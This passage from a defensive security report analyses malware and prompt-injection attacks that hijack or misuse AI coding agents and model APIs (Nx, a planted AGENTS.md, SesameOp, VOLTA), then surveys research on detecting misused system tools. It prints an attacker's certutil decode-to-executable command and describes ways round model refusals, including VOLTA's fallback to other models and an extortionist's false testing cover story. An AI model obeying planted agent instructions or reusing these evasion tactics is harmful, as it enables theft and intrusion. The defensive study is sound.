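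An attacker can also leave instructions for an agent to find. *AGENTS.md in Downloads* (David, 2026) reports that the security company Forever Security found a planted AGENTS.md file in a customer's Downloads folder that October. Coding agents look for files with that name and treat them as guidance. This one told the agent to install a known malicious npm package. Forever Security says it stopped the agent before any of the package's code ran, but could not determine how the file got there. In the company's own tests, similar files took over both Codex and Claude Code. A rule written for the Nx attack would not have caught this one, because the agent would have started npm, as it normally does.

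### Why checking the agent's identity would not have helped

If the victims' employers had required every agent to prove its identity before using a model, Claude Code would have passed on each machine, because it was the genuine program running on the right laptop under the right employee's account. The malware could start the real agent and give it a prompt, so it did not need to impersonate one or steal its credentials.

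Identity checks are good at catching counterfeit or unregistered programs, but a hijacked agent is neither. In the CyberProof case, too, the signed agent was exactly what the customer had approved.

Checking the origin of the Nx package would have been far more useful. According to Snyk, recent legitimate versions had provenance attestations, and the malicious ones did not. The Nx team identified the malicious releases by this difference. But npm did not require provenance, so it installed them. If it had rejected Nx releases without provenance, the install script would not have reached the agents.

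Two other safeguards stopped some of the agents. The models refused some prompts because of their content, and some copies of Claude Code rejected the permission-bypass flag until the user had approved it. Neither safeguard depended on the agent's identity. The second crudely tested whether the user had agreed, which is closer to the check that was missing in this attack. No developer had asked for the search, so proof of who authorised an action would address that gap more directly.

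### Which trace differed, who could see it, and how soon

On the victim's machine, the clearest difference from legitimate use was that a package's install script had started a coding agent, switched off its approval requests and told it to look for sensitive files. An EDR product on macOS or Linux could have recorded all of this as soon as the agent started, if it kept process ancestry and full command lines. Flagging it would have required a detection rule that few security teams had reason to write. Kurmi calls this the first known case of malware using developers' AI tools in this way.

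The model providers received the prompts just as quickly, and their models sometimes refused them because of the content alone. But the providers could not tell from the account that an install script had sent them.

Outsiders could notice the attack without access to any victim's machine. Anyone could see on npm that provenance was missing from the first malicious release onward, and a member of the Nx community reported suspicious behaviour about two hours after that release. GitHub could see the new repositories as the malware created them, and it restricted access to them at 9:05 am UTC, about ten and a half hours after the first malicious release.

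Many employers found out much later. The malware often published the data under employees' personal GitHub accounts, which the companies' own logs did not cover. When Wiz contacted more than 50 heavily affected organisations, the vast majority said this was their first indication of the attack. Almost 90 percent of the leaked GitHub tokens still worked more than 24 hours after GitHub took the repositories down.

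## Malware that talks to a trusted AI service: SesameOp

In July 2025, Microsoft's incident response team found a backdoor that Microsoft named SesameOp. A backdoor is a program that gives intruders continuing access to a computer. The intruders used OpenAI's service for command and control, which means sending instructions to infected computers and getting the results back. SesameOp did not use any of OpenAI's models.

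The Nx malware started real agents, so their connections to model providers were ordinary agent traffic. SesameOp had no agent, and its traffic resembled an agent's only in its destination, but the destination is most of what a network monitor can observe.

### How the backdoor used OpenAI

Malware has traditionally contacted a server that the attacker runs, which defenders can block once they know its address. SesameOp instead contacted OpenAI's Assistants API, a service for building custom AI assistants. Developers created an assistant with a name, a description and instructions, then exchanged messages with it. OpenAI stored all of this in the developer's account, and the intruders needed only that storage, which any program with the right API key could read or add to.

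According to Microsoft, the backdoor had an API key built in and worked in these steps:

1. It checked whether the account already had an entry for the infected computer, and created one if not.
2. It downloaded the account's list of assistants and read their descriptions. "SLEEP" meant that it should wait, and "Payload" meant that a command was ready.
3. It used the assistant's instructions field to find the message that held the command. It then deleted both the message and the assistant.
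4. It decrypted the command and ran it on the infected computer.
5. It encrypted the output, posted it as a new message and created an assistant with the description "Result", so the intruders would know to collect it.

SesameOp does not use a model at any step. Its main component was named OpenAIAgent, but Microsoft found that it used neither OpenAI's agent software nor the features that run models. OpenAI gave the same account in a statement to Infosecurity Magazine (*OpenAI Assistants API Exploited in 'SesameOp' Backdoor*), and added that any web service could be abused in this way. The Nx malware, for example, used GitHub to carry stolen data. OpenAI scheduled the Assistants API to be retired in August 2026, which would end this method, but attackers can use many other services that store text for their customers.

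### How responders found it

The intruders had been in the victim's network for several months before Microsoft's team arrived. Microsoft concluded that they wanted long-term access for espionage.

The responders first found a set of web shells, which are scripts on a server that run whatever commands someone sends them. Malicious processes elsewhere in the network were relaying commands to these web shells. The processes were utilities from Microsoft's programming software, Visual Studio, that the intruders had set up to load malicious libraries. The responders then searched for other Visual Studio utilities loading unusual libraries and found files that could communicate outside the network, including SesameOp.

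The useful clue was a trusted program loading code that did not belong to it. Nothing in Microsoft's account suggests that the connections to OpenAI had raised an alarm at the victim or at OpenAI. Microsoft doesn't say how long SesameOp had been running, and the intruders may have added it late in the intrusion.

Microsoft shared its findings with OpenAI, which identified and disabled an API key and its account. The account had made a limited number of API calls and had never used a model. A real customer would presumably have used a model, so it is less likely that the intruders had stolen the key from one.

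### What the network, the machine and OpenAI could each record

A network monitor would have recorded an encrypted connection to api.openai.com. SesameOp used the computer's normal web proxy unless its settings named another, so its traffic may well have passed through the same equipment as everyone else's. At a company whose employees use ChatGPT or coding agents, one more connection to OpenAI would hardly stand out. Regular contact through the night might look odd, but background agents and scheduled jobs also produce this pattern.

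Decrypting the traffic would have helped more than it usually does, because the company could have noticed a program using the Assistants API with a key that wasn't its own. The company still could not have read the commands, because SesameOp encrypted them separately.

The machine could record which process opened the connection and which libraries that process had loaded. Microsoft published a search that lists the name of every process that contacted api.openai.com, with the number of devices and days for each. A web browser would appear on hundreds of devices, whereas a programming utility that appears on only two would be worth investigating. An employee's home-made script would also be rare, so an analyst would have to go through the list. Canale and Soulis' agent detector might also have flagged SesameOp if the backdoor's commands started a shell. The agent label would have been wrong,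 but the alert would have given an analyst a reason to examine the program.

OpenAI had the key, the account and everything stored in it. It could have noticed that somebody kept creating and deleting assistants without ever running one, that each assistant's description was always one of three words, and that the messages were unreadable. A developer testing the service might do any one of these things, but the combination is strange enough to justify a review. Because the account made few calls, a provider would probably find this pattern only by looking for it.

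### What a provider can learn from an account

A provider can compare activity across victims. SesameOp created an entry in the OpenAI account for each infected computer, based on the computer's name, so the account held a list of victims. If those computers belonged to several organisations, OpenAI could have found the same key in use on unrelated networks, which no single victim could have known. Microsoft and OpenAI have not said how many computers were infected.

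The provider can also act for all the victims at once, while each victim can only clean its own machines. When OpenAI disabled the key, every copy of the backdoor that relied on it would have lost contact with the intruders.

But using one API key on many unrelated networks does not prove an attack. A small software company might sell a program with its own key inside, and its customers' computers would produce much the same pattern. Those customers chose to install the program, but OpenAI could not tell that from the account.

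Someone therefore had to bring evidence from the victim's side. A responder could find the API key in the backdoor's settings, but only OpenAI could look up the account it belonged to. As far as anyone has said, OpenAI had no reason to suspect that account until Microsoft got in touch.

The provider learns far more when attackers do use a model. Anthropic's August 2025 threat report describes an extortionist who ran Claude Code on Kali Linux, an operating system for security testing. The extortionist used Claude Code to carry out intrusions, analyse stolen financial data and decide how much ransom to demand. In a file of standing instructions, the extortionist gave Claude the cover story that this was network security testing under official support contracts. Real security testers have such contracts, and a provider cannot tell from the text alone whether a contract exists. The ransom notes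 were much harder to explain as testing, but the attacker already had the data by then.

### Malware that does query a model

Malware that sends requests to a model while it runs has since become more common. *Introducing CAIRN* (Fetterman, 2026) describes a toolkit for finding and tracking such malware, which the security company Cisco Talos released in September 2026. The toolkit soon found VOLTA, a Windows program that steals passwords, login sessions and cryptocurrency wallets.

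VOLTA sends a profile of each victim to a model, by default Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6, and asks what the victim is worth. *Appraisal by AI* (Fetterman, 2026) explains that the program checks the reply for phrases like "I can't". If it finds one, it tries Moonshot's Kimi K2 and then Google's Gemini 2.5 Flash. The results go to the criminal customer through Telegram (Cornelißen, *Infostealer VOLTA lässt Claude Beute bewerten*, 2026). VOLTA is not an agent, because the model does not choose what the program does next.

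VOLTA's network trace is different from SesameOp's. VOLTA sends its requests through a reseller, OpenRouter, so a monitor would record OpenRouter's address and not Anthropic's. OpenRouter knows which customer account made the request. Anthropic presumably receives the request from OpenRouter's servers and knows much less about where it came from, but it does see the text. The text is incriminating because it includes a stranger's home address and employer and a request to rank their valuables.

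An alert on the connection to OpenRouter would come too late to prevent the theft, because VOLTA contacts the model only after it has collected the data. Blocking OpenRouter would not prevent it either, because the AI step is optional according to Tom's Hardware's *New AI-driven Windows malware feeds stolen data to Claude*. But VOLTA deletes itself when it finishes, so a stored record of the connection could be one of the few signs that it was there.

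The model has a larger role in other recent malware. *Researchers uncover malware that uses AI to choose its next move* (Markovic, 2026) describes a program that is closer to being an agent. *NIK C2* (Raghuprasad, 2026) describes a command-and-control framework with AI built in, which Cisco Talos has seen in real use.

### Making approved traffic recognisable

A defender can learn very little from a connection to OpenAI as long as any program on the network can use any account. An organisation can change this by making its approved agents connect in a way that other programs cannot easily copy.

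A company can route the model requests of all approved agents through a gateway, a server that forwards them to the provider. The gateway holds the provider's API key, and the agents need only a credential for the gateway. The company can then block all other connections to the providers' APIs. On such a network, the firewall would have blocked SesameOp's calls to api.openai.com and logged each attempt. The gateway also receives the text of each request, so the company can see much of what the provider sees of its agents' activity.

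Codex and Claude Code both support routing through a gateway. Cloudflare's *OpenAI Codex* explains how to route Codex through Cloudflare's gateway with a profile that the user names when starting the agent. A user who leaves out the profile would presumably connect directly, so the company still needs to block direct connections. Anthropic documents the request formats that Claude Code can use with a gateway. In the formats for Amazon's and Google's clouds, Claude Code sends only the features that those clouds accept.

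A company can also tie its keys to its own network or machines:

- With OpenAI's *IP allowlist*, OpenAI rejects a valid key if the request comes from an address that the company has not listed. Anthropic's *Restrict access to Claude with IP allowlisting* (2026) describes a similar control for Enterprise plans.
- With OpenAI's *Mutual TLS*, a program must present a certificate as well as the key, so a thief who has only the key cannot use it.
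- OpenAI lets Codex use short-lived tokens from the company's identity system in place of a fixed key. The tokens in its example last ten minutes.
- Google is replacing the old keys for its Gemini API with ones that belong to a specific service account, and set September 2026 as the date to start rejecting the old kind. Truffle Security's *Google Fixes the Gemini API Key Privilege Escalation Issue* explains the reason. Keys that companies had made public for services like Google Maps could silently gain access to Gemini.

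All of these stop outsiders from using the company's account. None would have affected SesameOp, which brought a key for a different account.

### Refusing other people's accounts

To stop a program like SesameOp at the provider, a company needs the provider to refuse requests from the company's network that use anyone else's account. Anthropic's *Enforce network-level access control with Tenant Restrictions* describes how this works for Claude. The company's proxy adds a line to every request listing the organisations whose accounts the company permits. Anthropic returns an error if the account behind the request doesn't belong to one of them. Anthropic tells companies to overwrite any list already in the request, which prevents a program on a laptop from supplying its own. The proxy has to decrypt the traffic to add or overwrite the list.

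OpenAI and Google have similar controls with narrower coverage, according to OpenAI's *Corporate Network Controls in ChatGPT Enterprise* and Google Cloud's list of supported services.

| Provider | What the company can restrict to its own accounts | A program using an outsider's API key |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | Claude's website, apps and API | Refused |
| OpenAI | ChatGPT's website and apps | Not covered |
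| Google | Google Cloud services, including the Vertex AI model service | Refused on Vertex AI; the list does not include the Gemini API |

Microsoft has a control of this kind for Copilot, which Trend Micro supports in its own security product.

OpenAI tells companies to apply its restriction only to chatgpt.com, and *Configure Custom Headers* (2026), a log of changes to Microsoft's documentation, gives the same scope. OpenAI does not appear to offer an equivalent for its API at api.openai.com, which SesameOp used. If somebody built the same backdoor on Anthropic's API, a company with Tenant Restrictions could have the backdoor's first request refused. For OpenAI's API, the company would need to block direct connections and use a gateway.

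Even for ChatGPT, the restriction takes extra steps. People can use ChatGPT without logging in, so the company has to block that separately. The desktop and mobile apps also reject unfamiliar certificates, so the company must add its own certificate to them before it can inspect their traffic.

### What these controls miss

These restrictions work only when traffic passes through the company's equipment. Anthropic explains in its documentation for government customers that the restriction applies only to requests the proxy has marked. A laptop on home Wi-Fi can use any account unless the employer forces its traffic through the proxy there too. SesameOp could also use a proxy the intruders chose, although a strict firewall would block that connection.

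An attacker can also get around a company's list of permitted Anthropic accounts by sending requests to a reseller such as OpenRouter, because Anthropic then never receives the list. The company could block OpenRouter if none of its approved agents need it, but there are many such services, and a determined attacker could set up a private one. An attacker could also run a model on the victim's machine, which requires no outside service. The company would then have to rely on the machine's records, which might show a very large model file or unusually heavy processor use.

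The most serious gap is theft of the approved credential. A list of allowed addresses blocks a thief who uses the key elsewhere, but malware on the developer's laptop sends its requests from the company's own address. A client certificate doesn't help if the malware can copy its private key. OpenAI doesn't check whether a certificate's issuer has revoked it, so after a theft the company has to replace or deactivate certificates in its OpenAI settings. A gateway keeps the provider's key off the laptop, but malware could still steal the gateway credential or, as in the Nx attack, start the approved agent. In both cases, the malicious requests would come through the approved gateway and from the approved account.

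### How soon anyone could have noticed

On the victim's machines, SesameOp differed from legitimate activity because a programming utility loaded an unfamiliar library and contacted OpenAI. An EDR product could have recorded this from the first connection. At OpenAI, it differed because the account stored encrypted messages and never ran a model, which would have become apparent after a few exchanges. A network monitor without decryption would have recorded almost nothing that distinguished the malware from legitimate traffic.

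The intruders had been present for several months before investigators found the malware, and the discovery started with the libraries. Other organisations did not have the findings, or the search for processes that contact OpenAI, until Microsoft published them on 3 November 2025. A company that blocks direct connections to model APIs would stop the malware's first attempt to connect without having to recognise it.

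## How misuse of built-in system tools is detected

A company can block direct connections to a model provider, but it can't remove most of the tools built into Windows or Linux, because administrators and other software need them. Researchers who study living off the land, the misuse of these tools, therefore try to separate malicious from legitimate uses of the same program. Their results also give the best indication of how well anyone can expect to judge an AI agent's commands.

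### Two commands for the same tool

Certutil is a Windows program for managing digital certificates, the files that let a computer prove its identity to others. Certificates are often sent as Base64, a way of writing any file as plain text, so certutil can turn Base64 text back into the original file, even if that file isn't a certificate. *Living-Off-The-Land Command Detection Using Active Learning* (Ongun, Stokes and colleagues, 2021) lists the attacker's command below as an example of misuse. The rest of the table is invented for illustration.

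| | Administrator's use | Attacker's use |
|---|---|---|
| Command | `certutil -decode server.b64 server.cer` | `certutil -decode b64file newFile.exe` |
| Parent process | A script that renews certificates | A word processor with an email attachment open |
| What happens next | The company's web server loads the certificate | The new program starts and contacts an unfamiliar server |

Both commands run the same signed Microsoft program with the same option, and only the file names differ. The attacker's command produces a program instead of a certificate, which is suspicious, although an unusual installer might unpack a program the same way. The parent process and later events are stronger evidence, but a detector has to connect several records to use them.

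The simplest detector is a hand-written rule, such as an alert whenever certutil decodes text into an .exe file. Ongun and colleagues note that such rules usually produce many false positives, because administrators and developers use the same functions. A command classifier is meant to improve on hand-written rules by learning from examples which combinations of words are suspicious.

### Turning a command into numbers

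Ongun and colleagues, most of them at Microsoft, built a classifier called LOLAL for certutil and four other Windows tools. LOLAL joins the command line of a new process to that of its parent, so it uses the first two rows of the table but not the third. It then works in four steps:

1. It splits the text at spaces and punctuation into tokens such as "certutil", "decode" and "exe".
2. It represents each token as 16 numbers, called an embedding. Tokens that appear in similar surroundings get similar numbers. The researchers trained the embeddings on unlabelled commands containing 358 million words, from computers running Microsoft's Defender for Endpoint.
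3. It gives each token a score from 0 to 1 for how strongly labelled examples link it to malicious use of that particular tool. For certutil, the name of the temporary folder scored 1 and "install" scored 0.01.
4. It takes the minimum, the maximum and a weighted average of the embeddings across the whole command, giving suspicious tokens more weight in the average. This always produces 48 numbers, however long the command is. Ten more record the number of tokens, the number of rare tokens, the three highest token scores and which of the five tools the command uses.

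A set of decision trees then uses these 58 numbers to label the command as harmless or as a malicious use of one of the five tools.

Two of the highest-scoring tokens were "aptsimulator" and "attackiq", which come from software that companies use to rehearse attacks, so the classifier had partly learned to recognise security teams' exercises. A real intruder would have no reason to type either name.

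The researchers had 1,987 labelled commands, 1,533 malicious and 454 harmless. They evaluated LOLAL using the F1-score, which combines precision (the share of alerts that are correct) and recall (the share of malicious commands caught). Its average F1-score was 0.96 with an embedding method called fastText and 0.94 with an older one, word2vec. The false positive rate (the share of harmless commands wrongly flagged) was 2.0 percent with fastText and 2.7 percent with word2vec.

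Certutil was the easiest tool to classify, with precision and recall of 0.99, but it also supplied over half of the labelled examples. The hardest was msbuild, which compiles software. LOLAL caught 85 percent of malicious msbuild uses, and even the security experts had trouble labelling msbuild commands from the text alone. Coding agents may be hard to judge for the same reason, since they routinely compile software.

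The 2.0 percent figure is hard to apply to an ordinary computer. Every labelled command had already triggered a hand-written rule, so the harmless ones were probably harder than most to tell from malicious ones. On the other hand, about three quarters of the labelled commands were malicious, while almost no commands on a working machine are.

### Choosing which commands an analyst should label

Labeling takes a lot of expert time because each command has to be investigated. LOLAL therefore uses active learning, which selects the commands whose labels would most improve the classifier. It selects commands for which the two most likely classes are almost equally probable, and commands that are very unusual for their assigned class. It takes some of both kinds from every class so that the analyst doesn't label only commands for the most common tool.

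In a simulation, the researchers started LOLAL with ten labelled commands and revealed five more labels in each round. They compared it with simpler ways of choosing which commands to label.

| How the system chose commands | F1-score after 10 rounds | F1-score after 20 rounds |
|---|---|---|
| Uncertain and unusual (LOLAL) | 0.85 | 0.91 |
| Uncertain only | 0.76 | 0.88 |
| Unusual only | 0.78 | 0.89 |
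| At random | 0.80 | 0.87 |

LOLAL did best, but after 20 rounds it was only four points ahead of random choice, about as much as the results varied from run to run. The choice of classifier mattered far more. When the researchers replaced the decision trees with logistic regression, a simpler statistical method, the score after 20 rounds was 0.57.

A real analyst also tested LOLAL over three rounds, labelling 50 commands in each. The analyst confirmed 58 percent of the selected malicious predictions in the first round, 63 percent in the second and 73 percent in the third. LOLAL selected difficult cases by design, so these figures understate its precision on ordinary ones. The improvement is encouraging, but there were only three rounds.

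### Adobe's detector

Adobe's security team worked on Linux commands and relied much more on what its analysts already knew. Boros, Cotaie and colleagues (2022), in *Machine Learning and Feature Engineering for Detecting Living off the Land Attacks*, listed the cues analysts look for, and their software tags each command with the cues it contains. The tags cover the program being run, its options, sensitive file locations, the kind of network address and known attack patterns. For example, a command that uses the networking tool netcat to give another computer a shell gets tags for netcat, the shell, the option that joins them and the type of address. The classifier receives only these tags, so an analyst can easily check why it flagged a command.

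The team took 1,609 malicious commands from public catalogues of misused tools and sampled 7.9 million commands from Adobe's own logs, which it assumed were harmless. Only 0.02 percent of the examples were malicious, which is much more realistic than LOLAL's mix. The best classifiers had an F1-score of 0.95. No single cue was enough to identify a malicious command. For example, the temporary folder appeared in 57 malicious commands and more than 2.1 million harmless ones.

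If precision and recall were both about 0.95, the detector would have raised roughly 80 false alarms on 7.9 million harmless commands, a false positive rate of 0.001 percent. That would be excellent, but two choices made the task easier. The team removed malicious examples that could equally have been normal administration, such as a command that lists a firewall's rules, and these are the cases that cause trouble in practice. It also removed duplicates from the logs, so a harmless command that runs thousands of times a day counted only once. In live use, misclassifying that command could produce thousands of alerts.

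A year later, Boros and Cotaie (2023), in *Deep Dive into Hunting for LotLs Using Machine Learning and Feature Engineering*, tripled the number of harmless examples to 24 million and used a neural network, raising the F1-score to 0.976. The old method, retrained on the new data, reached 0.965. They then removed one kind of tag at a time from the old method. Its score fell to 0.79 without the analysts' attack patterns, while removing any other kind of tag lowered it by about 0.05 at most. Much of the detector's accuracy therefore depended on patterns written by analysts, who have to keep adding to them as attackers find new uses for old tools.

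### High scores and missed attacks

A detector can have high overall accuracy and still miss many attacks. *SENTINEL* (Shoeb, Hasan and colleagues, 2026) compared several classifiers on Windows commands, with about 15 harmless commands for every malicious one. One classifier, which used an older language model called BERT, correctly labeled about 99.3 percent of the commands in the validation set. Overall accuracy is a poor measure with so few malicious examples, because a program that called every command harmless would be right about 94 percent of the time. A second test mixed 50 commands from published accounts of Volt Typhoon, a Chinese state-sponsored campaign against US infrastructure, with 50 harmless uses of the same tools. The BERT classifier caught only 58 percent of the Volt Typhoon commands.

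SENTINEL, the researchers' own detector, adds three components to BERT: one reads individual characters, one compares up to five commands from the same hour, and one looks for unusual commands. It caught 94 percent of the Volt Typhoon commands but also flagged 10 percent of the harmless ones, which would make it unusable on a busy network.

At a stricter false positive rate of 0.1 percent, SENTINEL caught 81.8 percent of malicious commands, and BERT caught 69.7 percent. These figures come from the easier validation set, which contained only about 990 harmless commands, so a rate of 0.1 percent means a single false alarm. That is too few to predict what would happen across millions of commands. Shoeb and colleagues acknowledge that nobody has yet tested SENTINEL on data from a whole enterprise.

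Sophos has data on about 50 million different command lines a day. Gelman and Bergeron (2025), in *Sophos AI at Black Hat USA ’25*, measured how often a classifier ranked a malicious command above a harmless one, where 1 is perfect and 0.5 is no better than chance. The classifier scored 0.998 on commands from the three weeks after its training period, but 0.61 on a set that experts had labelled, drawn partly from real incident investigations.

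Training the classifier on more unusual but harmless commands raised the second score to 0.89. Anomaly detection, which looks for anything out of the ordinary, found candidates, and OpenAI's o3-mini model labeled them. Human experts checked a week of these labels and found the "harmless" ones almost always correct. Anomaly detection on its own produced too many false alarms to be worth running, but it was much more useful for finding strange, legitimate commands to train the classifier on.

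*Democratizing ML for Enterprise Security* (2025) describes a system that generates training examples instead of waiting for real ones. A language model writes both harmless and malicious commands for the same Windows tools, and a second step checks whether each command fits its label. This could help with tools that attackers rarely misuse. But the malicious commands may not be ones an attacker would type, so the resulting classifier still needs to be tested on real intrusions.

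### Why most alerts are false

A classifier that scores very well can still overwhelm its users with false alarms. Stamp (2022), in *Living-off-the-Land Abuse Detection Using Natural Language Processing and Supervised Learning*, built a classifier to detect abuse of 16 Windows tools, with an average F1-score of 0.99. In a test on a virtual machine, it flagged all 83 malicious commands, though some came from its training data, while Windows Defender caught eight. But when Stamp ran it on live commands from many computers, it produced far more false alarms than he had expected.

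He attributes this to the base-rate fallacy, the mistake of ignoring how rare something is when judging a test for it. Suppose that a large company's computers run 10 million harmless commands a day and 200 malicious ones. Its detector catches 90 percent of the malicious commands and has a false positive rate of 0.1 percent. These figures are only illustrative, but they give the following result:

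| | Commands a day | Alerts a day |
|---|---|---|
| Malicious | 200 | 180 |
| Harmless | 10,000,000 | 10,000 |
| Total | 10,000,200 | 10,180 |

Only 180 of the 10,180 alerts, or 1.8 percent, are real. Spending five minutes on each alert would take analysts about 850 hours every day. Catching every malicious command would raise the share of real alerts only to 2.0 percent. For half of the alerts to be real, the false positive rate would have to fall to 0.0018 percent, or about one false alert per 55,000 harmless commands.

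Stamp recommends that such detectors not raise alerts directly, or at least that companies filter the results first. He would rather have analysts sift through false positives than make the detector stricter and miss real attacks. That is reasonable for a few hundred alerts a day but not for 10,000.

A second check can greatly increase the share of alerts that are real. If it kept 90 percent of the real alerts in this example and dismissed 99 percent of the false ones, 162 real alerts and 100 false ones would remain, so 62 percent would be real. But the second check has to use different evidence, because if one text classifier misclassifies a harmless command, another may well do the same. The most obvious evidence to use is context that isn't in the command's text.

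### Baselines for machines, people and jobs

A baseline is a record of what is normal for a particular machine, account or role. Certutil might run every night on a server that manages certificates but never on an accountant's laptop, so running it on the laptop would be worth investigating.

CISA and its partner agencies recommend recording which tools administrators normally use, which commands they type, when they work and which machines they connect to. Programs also usually start in a fixed order when somebody logs in, so the same sequence in the middle of the afternoon could be suspicious. Accounts used by automated tools should be easier to profile, because the tools tend to run at set times and connect to the same machines.

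Some expectations about normal behaviour don't require records of past activity. In CISA's examples, a typical business user never opens a command prompt, and the accounts that administer a whole Windows network should log in only to the servers that control it. A company can also make normal behaviour simpler by choosing a small set of administrative tools and blocking or flagging the rest. This probably helps more than a more sophisticated detector, because it reduces the number of harmless commands that look suspicious.

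*SCADE* (2024) describes a detector for data centres that combines two baselines. One measures how rare a command is across the whole system, and the other records what is usual for each user and machine. A maintenance command that only one engineer runs every Friday would be rare overall but normal for that engineer.

Baselines have several practical problems. The security team has to know what administrators normally do, but CISA finds that security teams and administrators often work separately. Logging has to be more detailed than the default, and the company should store the logs where an intruder can't alter them. Someone also has to update the baseline whenever people change jobs or adopt new software. If an intruder was already active when the baseline was recorded, it may include the attack. CISA does not consider any of its recommendations foolproof.

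### Chains of events in a provenance graph

A provenance graph links system events by cause and effect, so it can include what happened after a command as well as what led to it. The graph represents each event as a subject, an operation and an object, such as "certutil writes newFile.exe" (Dong, Li and colleagues, 2023, *Are we there yet?*). Processes, files and network addresses are the nodes, and operations are the arrows between them.

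The attacker's use of certutil produces a graph with five nodes: the word processor, certutil, the file newFile.exe, the process that runs this file, and the unfamiliar server. The administrator's use also produces five nodes: the renewal script, certutil, the certificate, the web server process, and the address of a regular customer. The two graphs have almost the same shape, so a detector has to measure how unusual each link is. The frequencies below are invented.

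| Link | Attacker's chain | How often | Administrator's chain | How often |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 to 2 | Word processor starts certutil | 1 in 100,000 | Renewal script starts certutil | 1 in 10 |
| 2 to 3 | Certutil writes a program | 1 in 1,000 | Certutil writes a certificate | 9 in 10 |
| 3 to 4 | The program starts | 1 in 2 | Web server loads the certificate | 1 in 2 |
| 4 to 5 | It contacts an unfamiliar server | 1 in 50 | Web server answers a regular customer | 9 in 10 |

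Multiplying the frequencies gives about 1 in 10 billion for the attacker's chain and 1 in 25 for the administrator's. Programs start and contact new servers all the time, so neither of the last two links would justify an alert by itself, but they matter here because of how the program arrived.

Real detectors are more elaborate. Some apply rules written by experts, for example by marking a file from the internet as untrusted and passing that mark to everything the file affects. Most of the recent ones learn what normal graphs look like and flag the parts of a graph that don't fit.

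Dong and colleagues interviewed ten managers of security teams, and all ten considered provenance-based products more effective than conventional EDR. Their main reason was that the graph connects related alarms and shows an analyst where the trouble began.

### What the graphs cost, and how often they are wrong

Those same managers worried about the cost. Dong and colleagues surveyed security engineers about what they would accept, then measured three well-known detectors on more than 300 computers belonging to a security company's customers.

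| | Acceptable | HOLMES | ProvDetector | UNICORN |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Alarms per computer per day | Under 0.1 | 12.1 | 56.3 | 0.13 |
| Nodes in the graph for one alarm | Under 50 | 81 | 5 | 17,853 |
| Server memory per computer | Under 20 MB | 84 MB | 240 MB | 219 MB |

For 300 computers, the acceptable number of alarms is 30 a day, but HOLMES would raise about 3,600. UNICORN came close to 30, but only because it reported a computer's entire graph as one alarm, so an analyst would have to search thousands of nodes for the attack. One manager tried provenance graphs for a customer with 1,200 computers, and the server ran out of memory after processing 40 of them.

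Collecting the events also slows the monitored machine. The engineers would accept a slowdown of 3 percent. On a machine with a single processor core, Auditd, a common Linux logging tool, added as much as 821 percent to the time a web server needed for each request. The effect was much smaller on larger machines and for programs that mainly do calculations.

False alarms remain a problem for newer detectors. Xiao, Jiang and colleagues (2026), in *How Far Should We Need to Go*, tested five of them on data from two commercial security services. They trained the detectors on one day of data from a Windows computer whose activity included something new every day, then tested them on the following week, which contained no attack. Three of the five had false positive rates above 23 percent.

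The causes were ordinary. A Windows process had run more than 2,000 scripts to collect hardware information, and someone had downloaded many images during an online meeting.

A detector called Orthrus had a false-alarm rate below 1 percent on that computer, but only because it flagged very little. It found one of 44 malicious items in another test and none of 16 in a real case of data theft. Nodlink, which gives more weight to the wording of commands, caught nearly all the malicious processes in the theft, but it also raised about 1,500 false alarms for 11 real ones. The thief had been on the machine before monitoring began, so the training data included the attack. Nodlink still flagged it because it was rare compared with everything else.

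Xiao and colleagues reduced Nodlink's false positive rate from about 25 to 10 percent by grouping similar processes and treating the large groups as harmless. An analyst could also check one process from each group, which would save about two thirds of the work. But the filter is useful only if it doesn't discard real attacks, and Xiao and colleagues leave that question to future research.

The fastest detector tested took about four seconds to check a graph with more than 600,000 elements on a powerful graphics processor, not counting the time to build the graph. An alert about a real attack would probably wait much longer than that for an analyst to review it.

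Published scores for these detectors need careful reading. Moon, Kim and Pyeon (2026), in *Where the Numbers Come From*, examined a detector called ThreaTrace, which has a precision of 0.938 if an alarm counts as correct whenever it is close to part of an attack in the graph. Only seven of its 994 alarms were on items labelled as part of the attack. Counting nearby alarms makes some sense, since an analyst who starts there may find the attack, but readers will expect "precision" to count only alarms on the attack itself.

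Moon and colleagues also found that researchers had used the test answers to choose the best version of a model. When Moon and colleagues removed that advantage, precision fell by 0.16 to 0.33 in the four set-ups they tried. In *How Benchmarks and Evaluation Protocols Shape Conclusions in Provenance-Based Intrusion Detection*, Guerra, Chapuis and colleagues (2026) warn that claims about which design works best can depend heavily on the data and test procedure.

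None of these tests involved an attacker trying to fool the detector. Attackers can defeat such detectors by imitating normal activity, a risk that Xiao and colleagues mention but did not test.

### What carries over to AI agents

The most useful lesson for detecting malicious agents is to judge a command by what came before and after it. In the Nx attack, a provenance graph would have connected the install script to the agent's file search. An install script launching an agent should be rare enough to produce a high anomaly score.

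The base-rate problem also applies to agents, which make it worse by running so many harmless commands. If they doubled the total in the earlier example to 20 million a day, false alarms would double and the share of alerts that were real would fall from 1.8 to 0.9 percent, even with the same attackers and detector.

Baselines work best when people have steady habits, as when an administrator tends to solve the same problem the same way each time. An agent writes new commands for each task and may change its approach when its developer updates the model. The Windows computer that did something new every day is probably the closest comparison in this research, although Xiao and colleagues were not studying agents.

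Detectors that look at sequences can also mistake coding agents for intruders. An administrator usually knows which tool to use, so somebody who tries one after another may be an intruder exploring an unfamiliar machine. Coding agents do this routinely. CraftedSignal (2026), summarising an analysis by Sophos, reports that they try several approaches when something fails, and that some download files with the same built-in Windows tools that attackers use.

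A company could keep a baseline for everything an agent starts, separate from the developer's own activity. This should work reasonably well for an agent that reviews code every night in an automated build, because its job is almost as predictable as renewing certificates. It would work much less well for an assistant on a laptop, because the developer may ask for something different every hour.

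## What endpoint security products record when the agent is legitimate

For seven days in June 2026, Sophos recorded the detection rules that coding agents triggered on its customers' Windows computers. Some of these rules block an action, and others only record it. Sophos grouped the detections by what each action would achieve in an attack. It counted computers instead of events, so an agent that repeated one command many times did not distort the result.

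Credential access (getting at stored passwords and keys) accounted for 56.2 percent of the hits on blocking rules, and execution (running code in a suspicious way) for 28.8 percent. Among the silent rules, evasion (avoiding security software) came first with 38.5 percent, followed by command and control with 34.0 percent and execution with 11.1 percent. An agent can trigger an evasion rule without hiding anything, because agents, like intruders, make network calls, start child processes and write odd command lines.

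### Decrypting browser data

One rule produced 42.6 percent of the credential hits. It fires when a program asks Windows to decrypt credentials saved by a browser. Windows ties the encryption to the user's login, so any program running as that user can make the request.

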